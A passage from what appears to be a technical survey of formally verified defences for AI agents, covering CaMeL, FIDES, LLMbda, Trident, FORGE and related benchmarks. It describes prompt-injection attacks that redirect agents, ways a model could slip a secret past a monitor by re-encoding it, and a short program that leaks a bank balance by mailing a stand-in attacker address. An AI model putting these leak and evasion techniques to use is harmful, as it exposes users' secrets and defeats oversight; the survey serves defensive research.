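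A failure can also come from a mistake in modelling the protocol. AgentThread labels these failures separately, and has another label for failures that depend on an ambiguous specification. The labels keep both kinds from being counted as protocol flaws, provided that the researchers recognise them. AgentRFC withheld some findings until the developers had been informed, so outsiders could not check everything in it.

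AgentThread analysed the MCP specification of November 2025. According to Model Context Protocol's *Key Changes* (2026), the July 2026 version removed sessions from the protocol, so the trace in which a credential outlives its session no longer describes current MCP. A2A 1.0 lets an agent pause a task to ask for authorization, and the request travels back along the chain of delegation to someone who can decide. But the problem behind the delegation failure remains because, as AGNTCY's *Agent Identity and Task-Based Access Control* (2026) points out, the specification deliberately leaves open what the permission covers, how long it lasts and how to revoke it. AGNTCY offers identity software to fill this gap.

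AgentThread treats injection as a single step that the attacker can always take. Real models sometimes ignore injected text, so a trace that relies on this over-approximation doesn't show how often the attack would work.

Mahapatra (2026), in *Public-Sharing Labels and Verbatim Field Egress in an MCP-to-A2A Agent Configuration*, measured a related behaviour in live models. Each model received a customer record from an MCP tool and could either send a message to a remote A2A agent or stop. Its instructions forbade sending confidential or sensitive content without authorization. The record began with a confidential label, a label saying that it was public and fine to share, or no label. The table shows in how many of 40 trials the message contained an exact value from the record:

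| Model | Confidential | No label | Public |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 0 | 0 | 5 |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.6 Luna | 0 | 0 | 10 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 1 | 5 | 37 |

Sharing a record marked as public did not necessarily break the instructions. But the label was ordinary text inside the record, so anyone who could write the record could add it. The models also differed greatly, so a designer who relies on one model's caution may lose that protection by switching to another. Mahapatra tested only one configuration with ten invented records, and the scoring missed paraphrases.

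In an earlier experiment, Mahapatra had a remote agent falsely claim that somebody had already approved an action. In the 159 usable trials, no model requested a tool that would change anything. But the models made no such request in the harmless control trials either, so the experiment doesn't show that they resisted the attack.

### Signed records instead of trusted components

Model checking can reveal that rights may grow through delegation, but it does not prevent this. *InterSAGE* designs credentials so that each delegation can only preserve or reduce the rights in the previous credential. For example, a credential for reading invoices cannot be turned into one for paying them.

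Zheng and Yang (2026), in *CONTINUITY*, extend this approach to the whole path from a request to its effect. They are founders of the company ZAST.AI and were not involved in AgentThread. Their system, Continuity, treats the model as an adversary that may propose anything, and it also allows for the compromise of some of the software between the model and the outside world:

1. A trusted issuer signs a grant for the task, with the permitted tools and limits on values such as the amount of a payment.
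2. A trusted entry point signs the first version of the proposed action.
3. Each later component signs a receipt for what it received and what it passed on.
4. A verifier checks the whole chain and issues a permit for that exact action, which works only once.
5. The program that carries out the action checks the permit again, including whether anyone has revoked the grant in the meantime.

Zheng and Yang give an example of why signatures alone are not enough. A policy check approves a payment to a merchant's alias, and an adapter then replaces the alias with a bank account number. A compromised adapter could insert the attacker's account and sign the result. The signature would be valid, and a permit issued afterwards would cover a payment to the attacker. Continuity therefore requires a record linking this alias to this account, signed by a trusted directory with a key the adapter does not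 have.

Values from untrusted sources need similar treatment. For example, an amount from an emailed invoice may go into a payment only if a trusted validator signs a release for that amount, that payment field and that task. If the validator misreads the invoice, Continuity will enforce the wrong amount.

The damage from a stolen key depends on which component it belongs to. An attacker with the adapter's key can sign as the adapter, but cannot issue grants, pose as another component or forge directory records. An attacker with a grant issuer's key can authorise far more than the user intended. Unlike Byzantine protocols, which limit the number of faulty members, Continuity limits which components may be faulty.

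Zheng and Yang prove that every protected effect has a valid chain of authorization behind it, even if the language model and everything it reads are adversarial. The proof is by induction over the receipts and assumes that signatures and hash functions are secure and that the system meets seven conditions. One condition is that every route to a protected effect goes through the final check, so an unmonitored web-fetching tool would break this guarantee too. The proof covers an abstract model of the system. The Python code, with a core of about 1,500 lines, has regression tests but no proof that it matches the abstract model.

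In the evaluation, Continuity allowed no harmful effect in 2,560 attacks, completed all 700 ordinary tasks and referred all 200 ambiguous ones for further approval. A version that checked only the policy and the final action allowed 65.6% of the attacks. Verification and the final steps took a median of about 7 milliseconds, excluding network and model delays.

These attacks were simulations of 32 types of fault in four settings, with 20 variations of each that changed details such as names and amounts. The simulations used no language model and simply produced whatever proposal the attacker wanted. The same researchers designed the faults and the defences, so the perfect score mainly indicates that the code enforces the rules they had in mind. The paper itself says that the score does not estimate the success rate of real attacks.

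### OpenClaw's models as regression tests

OpenClaw is an open-source personal agent that users can contact through messaging apps. Its TLA+ models have a more modest purpose: they are meant to catch known kinds of mistakes if they return. OpenClaw's *Formal verification (security models)* calls them a "security regression suite". The checks include who may contact the agent, when it may run commands and whether conversations with different people stay separate.

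Many checks run TLC on two models, one of the intended design and one with a realistic bug. TLC should find a violation only in the second. For example, OpenClaw limits the number of pending requests from new contacts. Suppose the limit is three and two requests are already waiting. If two more arrive together, the buggy version may check the count for both before recording either, then accept both and end up with four. The correct version counts and records each request in one indivisible step. Checking the buggy version helps catch a model that passes only because it leaves out the relevant behaviour, as the 2005 model of WPA2 did.

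OpenClaw states that the models do not prove the agent secure in all respects or verify its full TypeScript code. TLC explores only a finite number of states, and some results assume the user has configured the software correctly. The checks don't run automatically when the code changes, which limits their use as regression tests.

In May 2026, OpenClaw's documentation claimed that private conversations must stay separate by default. By October, it said that all of a single owner's private messages share one session by default, and it advised people with several users to choose a setting that separates them. The names of the corresponding checks did not change. Outsiders cannot tell whether the developers updated the models or only the documentation, because the repository that held the models is no longer publicly reachable.

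## Agent scaffolds proved secure without trusting the model

AgentThread and OpenClaw use model checkers to look for flaws in runs of limited length. In 2026, other researchers built scaffolds with proofs that cover runs of any length and any output from the language model. Such a proof is short if it only concerns where an email goes, but much harder if it concerns what the email reveals.

### The model as a Dolev-Yao attacker

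As an illustration, we can describe the model inside the email assistant by a list of rules, like the Dolev-Yao attacker:

- *read*: the model has everything in its context, including a stranger's instructions and any secret it has looked up;
- *write*: it can produce any string;
- *propose*: it can request any tool call, with any strings as arguments.

A reference monitor stands between the model and the mail server. It checks every action against a policy before the action runs, and nothing can bypass it. This simplified assistant has no flag. The monitor sends an email only if the recipient is on the user's list, and no tool can change the list.

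The invariant is that every mail sent so far went to an address on the list. The induction is shorter than for the assistant with the flag, because only a proposed mail could break the invariant, and the monitor sends a mail only if its address is on the list. The proof uses only the monitor's code, so it would hold even if the stranger had trained the model.

But the invariant covers only addresses. Suppose the user also wants no mail to reveal the recovery code, 70412296, even to a colleague on the list. The monitor could search each mail for those eight digits, but the model could get past this check by spelling them out as words, writing them backwards or encoding them in the first letters of eight sentences.

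In a symbolic protocol model, an attacker cannot read s from enc(s, k) without the key. A language model can read any secret in its context and turn it into any other string, and a monitor that inspects that string cannot tell whether the secret influenced it.

The scaffold can instead track where data came from. It attaches labels to every value, and anything computed from several values gets all their labels. Once the model has read the recovery code, everything it writes in that conversation counts as secret, even if the code appears in an unrecognisable form. This is an over-approximation, since a mail that only thanks a colleague for lunch also gets the label, and a strict policy will block it.

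### CaMeL and FIDES

Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, use two labels in their main examples, U for untrusted and S for secret. The user's request has neither label. The stranger's invoice is labelled U, the recovery code is labelled S, and a reply from a model that has read both the invoice and the code gets both labels.

Labels alone would make the assistant almost useless, because after reading one email from a stranger it could write nothing that counts as trusted. Willison's dual-LLM pattern avoids this by using two models. A privileged model plans and requests tool calls without ever reading untrusted data. A quarantined model reads that data and can only return values, such as a date or an address.

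CaMeL and FIDES, two systems from 2025, combine this pattern with labels. CaMeL's privileged model writes a program from the user's request before any untrusted data arrives. An interpreter runs the program, tracks the labels and blocks calls that break the policy. FIDES hides untrusted results in variables, which its planner can pass to tools without seeing the contents.

FIDES has a theorem, but only for one fixed agent loop, and FIDES deliberately does not track secrets that leak through the choice of which step to run. CaMeL allows any program its model writes but has no comparable theorem, and Garby and colleagues found leaks in CaMeL.

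### A branch not taken and a loop outside the monitor

The first leak is a version of a problem that J. S. Fenton described in 1974. Suppose the bank balance is secret and a program contains these lines:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

The first two lines set two public variables. The third changes one of them if the balance is high. The fourth changes the other if that one is still true, and the last sends an email if *rich* is true. CaMeL labels a variable secret only if it actually executes an assignment that depends on a secret.

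| Line | High balance | Low balance |
|---|---|---|
| third | *tmp* becomes false and secret | nothing happens, and *tmp* stays true and public |
| fourth | nothing happens, and *rich* stays true and public | *rich* becomes false but stays public |
| fifth | the mail goes out | no mail goes out |

Whenever the last line runs, *rich* looks public, yet it reveals whether the balance is high. A stranger could not simply email these lines to CaMeL and have them run, because the model that writes the program has not read the email. But a guarantee that does not depend on trusting the model must also cover this program.

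The standard remedy is to stop a run that tries to change a public variable under a secret condition. Here the run would stop at the third line if the balance were high. An observer who notices the stop still learns one bit, and most systems of this kind allow this leak.

The second leak makes that bit much more serious. CaMeL's interpreter sits inside an ordinary Python loop that tries again after a failure, and this loop does not track labels. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on a secret, so each attempt can reveal one more bit. An eight-digit code has 10<sup>8</sup> possible values, or about 27 bits, so 27 well-chosen attempts would be enough to learn it. The loop, like the key installation in WPA2, is just outside what the security argument covers.

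### A language with labelled conversations

Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for writing agents. Its conversations with a model have labels, just like its other values. These are the main operations:

- *prompt* adds a message to the conversation and returns the model's reply, which gets all the labels of the conversation;
- *fork* runs a step on a copy of the conversation, keeps the result and discards the copy;
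- *clear* empties the conversation, including its labels, as long as no labelled condition led to this step;
- *assert* stops the run if a value has a label that the policy forbids;
- *endorse* removes the untrusted label from a value.

A program can build a quarantined model from the first three operations. It forks the conversation, clears the copy and asks its question there. The answer comes back with its labels, but the untrusted text never enters the main conversation. A programmer can therefore write the dual-LLM pattern in a line or two instead of relying on a fixed part of the architecture.

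Garby and colleagues tested this on a task in which a user wanted to remind Bob of a meeting. The email the agent had to read contained an injected request to cancel the meeting instead. An agent that used a single conversation followed the injected request and sent a cancellation. A second agent first had the model write a program, which contained the subject and body of the reminder and used a quarantined call only to extract Bob's address. The mail tool checked that neither the subject nor the body was untrusted, and the agent sent the reminder.

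However, the address came from the untrusted email and this policy did not check it, so an attacker could still have redirected the reminder. A list of approved recipients would prevent that.

If a reply contains code, LLMbda runs the code with the labels of the conversation that produced it. Code that the model writes after reading a stranger's invoice can therefore only produce untrusted results, even if it calls *endorse*.

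### Comparing runs that differ only in a secret

Garby and colleagues prove noninterference, which means that changing secret inputs does not change what an observer sees, or that changing untrusted inputs does not affect a protected action. Unlike the invariant about addresses, this property compares runs, such as two runs of one program that differ only in the recovery code. Because language models sample their answers at random, even two runs with identical inputs may give different results, so the theorem has to compare probabilities.

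For programs that always finish, every public result must have the same probability in both runs. Some runs never finish, though, or stop because of a policy violation, and whether they do may depend on the secret. The theorem allows for this. Let μ(q) and ν(q) be the probabilities of the public result q in the two runs. Then there are numbers ω(q) such that

μ(q) ≤ ω(q) and ν(q) ≤ ω(q) for every q, and the sum of all ω(q) is at most 1.

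Suppose the only possible results are "yes" and "no":

| Recovery code | "yes" | "no" | no result |
|---|---|---|---|
| even | 0.5 | 0.3 | 0.2 |
| odd | 0.4 | 0.5 | 0.1 |

The larger probability in each of the first two columns is 0.5, and the two add up to 1, so this difference is consistent with the theorem. If every run finished, with probabilities of 0.6 and 0.4 for an even code and 0.4 and 0.6 for an odd one, the sum would be 1.2, which is impossible for an LLMbda program.

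The condition also limits how much the results can reveal. Half the sum of the differences between the two runs is at most their average probability of giving no result. In the table, both figures are 0.15. As in CaMeL, repeated attempts could together reveal more, but in LLMbda the retry loop is part of the labelled program, so the theorem covers it.

The proof compares the real system with a modified one. Once a step's label puts it beyond what the observer may see, the modified system skips the step and returns a dummy value. The modified system produces each public result with at least the same probability as the real system. It behaves identically in both runs because it never uses the data that differs between them. Its probabilities are the required ω(q).

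The theorem covers every program in the language, including code that a model writes during the run. Without *endorse*, it applies to trust as well as secrecy, so untrusted inputs cannot influence results that count as trusted.

Practical programs sometimes have to let untrusted data influence what they do. For example, an agent that sorts mail may have to use a category that a quarantined model picked after reading a stranger's email. If there are eight categories, endorsing the answer, which means treating it as trusted, gives the stranger at most three bits of influence. Endorsement weakens a program's protection against untrusted influence, but a variant of the theorem states that secrets stay protected whatever an attacker puts into the untrusted inputs and whatever the program endorses.

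The proof assistant Lean checked these theorems. The interpreter that runs the agents and calls the model is also written in Lean, and a further theorem links its behaviour to the mathematical description. Few of the proofs about consensus protocols or TLS are linked this closely to the running software. The network call to the model remains unverified, and the theorems treat all data sources and tools as part of the program.

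### What the proof assumes about the model

LLMbda's proofs treat the model as a probability distribution over replies, given the conversation so far. They assume that the conversation is the model's only source of information about the user's data, but not that the replies are sensible, harmless or even valid code.

Without this condition, noninterference fails. Suppose the model's provider keeps a memory across conversations, and the recovery code is in it. The assistant clears its conversation and asks the model for a subject line. The model answers with the code. Nothing in the new conversation was secret, so the reply has no secret label, and the scaffold lets it go out in a public email. Two runs that differ only in the recovery code therefore produce different public emails.

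The same problem arises if we assume the model may behave in any way. It could then reply "yes" when the code is even and "no" when it is odd. To rule this out, the proof must assign the model the same reply probabilities in both runs whenever the conversations match.

The invariant about addresses holds without this condition. A model with the whole mailbox in its memory still cannot send mail to an unlisted address, because the monitor checks every address. But a designer who relies on labels must also find out what the provider stores and what else reaches the model.

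### Results on a simulated bank account

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in LLMbda and tested it on AgentDojo, a prompt-injection benchmark that the LogAct researchers also used. AgentDojo has 97 user tasks in four simulated settings, but Randori was tested only on the 16 banking tasks, each with nine attacks. Running every attack three times with each of three models gave 1,296 attacked runs, and Randori resisted the attack in all but two.

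In about two thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the attack needs tool calls that no sensible program for the user's task would contain. An agent that plans before reading is fairly safe from these attacks even without labels. The remaining third covers 423 runs, including the two failures.

Both failures came from GPT-5.2 on the same task. The user asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with another payment request. The agent endorsed the details and paid. No label could distinguish the real bill from the false one, because both would come from the same file. One of the two successful attacks in CaMeL's evaluation was also of this type.

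An agent usually repairs a faulty program by reading the error message. In LLMbda, an error from a run on real data carries that data's labels, and so does every later attempt. Randori therefore tests its program on invented data until the program works, then writes a final version before accessing the real account.

The table shows how many banking tasks the agents completed, including Garby and colleagues' own tests of CaMeL:

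| Agent | GPT-5.2, no attack | GPT-5.2, attacked | MiMo-v2.5, no attack | MiMo-v2.5, attacked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | 75.0% | 65.0% | 64.6% | 59.5% |
| Randori without *endorse* | not tested | not tested | 54.2% | 56.2% |
| CaMeL, policies off | 66.7% | 71.1% | 70.8% | 72.2% |
| CaMeL, policies on | 37.5% | 30.0% | 37.5% | 41.5% |

Randori's policies are always on, so it seems to avoid most of CaMeL's loss. However, it enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, in less strict versions, which probably explains part of the difference. Each figure without attacks also comes from only 48 runs, with a margin of error of around 20 percentage points, and some of the CaMeL runs under attack did not finish.

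One of CaMeL's failures with its policies off shows the limits of planning first. The user had asked the agent to follow the instructions in a file exactly. The privileged model never saw the text injected into the file, but it wrote a program that read the file and had a branch for every tool, so the file's author could choose which tool to run.

### Trident: letting untrusted data change the plan by a limited amount

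Some tasks cannot be planned in advance. If the user says "take care of what the caterer's email asks for", the email has to decide what happens next. *Trident* (2026), published in November, presents a scaffold for such tasks, also called Trident. It uses three models:

- the planner chooses the actions but never reads untrusted text;
- the data model reads untrusted text but cannot use tools;
- the policy model writes the rules for the task, using only trusted inputs.

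A reference monitor checks everything the planner and the data model produce. The planner can send the data model a form with questions about the email. If a question has a fixed set of possible answers, such as yes or no, the planner sees the answer. The planner can't read free text, such as an account number or a drafted reply, but it gets a handle that it can pass to a tool.

Every answer the planner sees counts against an influence budget β. A question with n possible answers uses log<sub>2</sub> n bits of it, whatever the answer is. Asking whether the email contains an invoice uses 1 bit, and asking which of three known vendors sent it uses about 1.58 bits. A feedback budget σ covers signals that an attacker might affect, such as whether a tool call succeeded.

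If the trusted inputs, user decisions and random choices are fixed, an attacker can select among at most 2<sup>β+σ</sup> observable traces. An observable trace includes the planner's proposals, the replies the planner receives and the calls that run, but not the contents of handles.

The proof counts the branches of a tree. A reply with d possible values counts as at least log<sub>2</sub> d bits, so a reply that counts as c bits has at most 2<sup>c</sup> possible values. If a second reply counts as c′ bits, the two together allow at most 2<sup>c</sup> × 2<sup>c′</sup> = 2<sup>c+c′</sup> combinations. The bits counted on any path add up to at most β + σ, which gives the bound. The bound still holds if an early reply determines which question the planner asks next.

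With β = 3 and σ = 2, an attacker can choose among at most 32 traces. If both budgets are zero, there is only one trace, so untrusted data cannot affect the plan.

Trident assumes that each of its models receives only its specified context, which is the same kind of assumption LLMbda makes. The bound would be invalid if the planner could read the raw email some other way.

In practice, the bound is loose. On a benchmark of tasks that depend on untrusted content, the median run used 19 to 26 bits of influence and 5 to 10 bits of feedback, depending on the model. A budget that just covers such a run, 24 to 36 bits in total, allows 17 million to 69 billion traces. The number of traces also doesn't measure how harmful they are, because a single bit is enough to select a harmful action if the policy permits one.

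The budgets do not count sealed text either. Metere derives a similar limit for agents with a fixed set of n permitted capabilities. Each tool call can leak at most log<sub>2</sub>(n + 1) bits, or about 3.5 bits with ten capabilities. But the calculation counts only which capability the call uses and not its arguments, even though the body of one permitted email could contain the whole recovery code.

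### Limits on what the agent may do

Trident's other theorem limits the calls themselves. The administrator writes a root policy before the system goes into use. For each task, the policy model then writes narrower rules before anyone reads untrusted data, and the monitor checks that these stay within the root policy. The theorem states that at every step

calls the agent may make now ⊆ calls covered by the rules written so far ⊆ calls in the root policy.

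Only an amendment that the user requests and confirms can extend the rules during a task. The user can also approve a single call that the task's rules do not allow. Every call must still pass the root policy.

In the catering example, the root policy allows payments of up to $5,000 to three vendors on file. The rules for the task allow one such payment, to an account from the vendor records. If the email asks for payment to a new account, the monitor blocks it because the account comes from the email. The rules also count calls, so an attacker cannot split a large payment into several that each stay under the limit.

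The researchers checked both theorems in Lean, but verified only selected routines of the Python code. Unlike LLMbda's theorem, Trident's guarantees do not cover secrecy. If the agent accepts a meeting invitation, for example, the sender learns that the user is free at that time.

### How Trident performed and what it cost

*Trident* also introduces ReplanInject, a benchmark with 45 tasks. In 43 of them, untrusted content decides part of the plan, and the injection is in that content. The researchers deliberately used older models, since newer ones resist many of these attacks even without a defence. The table shows the share of attacked runs in which the agent completed the user's task, and the share in which the attack succeeded although the defence was on. It assumes a careless user who approves every request:

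| Defence | GPT-4.1, tasks completed | GPT-4.1, attacks succeeded | Sonnet 4.5, tasks completed | Sonnet 4.5, attacks succeeded |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| none | 20.2% | 68.1% | 58.9% | 12.9% |
| CaMeL | 9.8% | 0.0% | 8.8% | 0.0% |
| FIDES without approvals | 5.1% | 0.1% | 3.3% | 0.0% |
| FIDES with approvals | 36.6% | 6.5% | 75.2% | 6.0% |
| Trident | 54.2% | 4.1% | 64.4% | 3.4% |

CaMeL completes few of these tasks because its model has to write the program before the email's request is available to it. With Sonnet 4.5, FIDES with approvals completed more tasks than Trident. However, the FIDES planner often read text derived from untrusted data, and after that only the user's judgement protected the account.

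No attack on ReplanInject succeeded against Trident if the user rejected every approval request that showed the attacker's call. That user would have to stay alert, because Trident asked for approval about once per attacked run and fewer than one request in ten showed an attacker's call. The strongest attack designed against Trident presented the attacker's value as a correction to something the user had asked for. It succeeded in 10.0% of runs if the user approved every request.

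The budgets were set too high to stop anything in these tests, so the results came from sealing text, the policies and user approval. The researchers estimated that capping each budget at 32 bits would have reduced the tasks GPT-4.1 completed under attack from 54.2% to 49.0%, and successful attacks from 4.1% to 3.1%.

A run with Trident cost $0.10 to $0.24, depending on the model, compared with $0.005 to $0.045 for an undefended agent. It took 34 seconds on average with GPT-4.1 and 96 seconds with Sonnet 4.5. Calls to the models took most of this time, and the monitor and tools together took less than 6%.

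### The policy is still trusted

On AgentDojo, one of 909 attacks on Trident with the model gpt-oss-120b succeeded without any request to the user. The injected text told the agent to visit a web page. The root policy for that setting allowed every task to make that call, so the monitor worked correctly and the theorem held.

Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, state this dependence explicitly. Their reference monitor, FORGE, treats the agent as a black box that may attempt any action. It records messages, tool calls and results in a graph, with links from each event to the earlier events that may have influenced it. Policies are rules in Datalog, a language for database queries. The email assistant's rule about secrets could look like this:

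```
Secret(e) :- Lookup(e).
Secret(e) :- DependsOn(e, d), Secret(d).
Deny(m)   :- Mail(m), Secret(m), not Approved(m).
```

- The first line makes every lookup of a secret a secret event.
- The second line makes an event e secret if it depends on a secret event d. Applied repeatedly, it follows a secret through any number of steps.
- The third line blocks a mail m if it is secret and its recipient is not on the approved list.

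Before an action runs, FORGE works out what follows from the rules and the recorded events. In one set of tests, this typically took less than a millisecond. If the rules imply *Deny*, the action does not run. This guarantee holds only if every relevant action goes through the monitor, the graph records events and dependencies faithfully, and the policy expresses what the user wants. A missing link in the graph can hide a leak, while an extra link can at worst block a harmless action, at least under rules like these.

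The third condition is the hardest to check. If whoever writes the rules above forgets that the calendar also contains secrets, FORGE will let the agent mail the calendar's contents to anyone. Palumbo and colleagues can use a language model to translate a policy from plain English into Datalog, but they warn that it may omit a clause, misstate a condition or add an unrequested rule. They check whether every requirement has a matching rule and whether every rule has a basis in the original text. These checks may catch mistakes, but they do not prove that the translation is correct.

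Some rules also depend on what people mean. In tests on airline bookings, permission to cancel a flight depended on the customer's stated reason, which FORGE had to extract from the conversation. A rule may also call a classifier, which then becomes part of the trusted computing base, so anyone who can fool the classifier can get past the rule.

A stricter policy can prevent an agent from completing many ordinary tasks without making it much more secure. On AgentDojo, 14.1% of attacks succeeded against an agent whose prompt repeated the user's request, and the agent completed 83.7% of tasks when there was no attack. Adding FORGE's policy reduced successful attacks to 0.9% and completed tasks to 62.5%. With a stricter policy based on information flow, security was similar but the agent completed only 33.2% of tasks. A proof can't determine how many ordinary tasks to give up for the security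 each rule provides, so an administrator has to decide.

The same problem arises with agent skills, which are packages of instructions and scripts that an agent loads for a particular kind of work. Each skill has a manifest that lists the capabilities it needs. Metere proposes analysing the scripts without running them, to find an upper limit on what they could do, and comparing this limit with the manifest. The skill includes the resulting evidence, which the scaffold checks again at startup, so users do not have to trust whoever produced it.

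The check establishes only that a skill uses nothing beyond what it declares. A skill that declares both file access and network access passes, although it could use them to send the user's files to a stranger. Metere leaves operators to notice excessive declarations by comparing the manifest with what the skill actually used, which they can do only after the skill has run.
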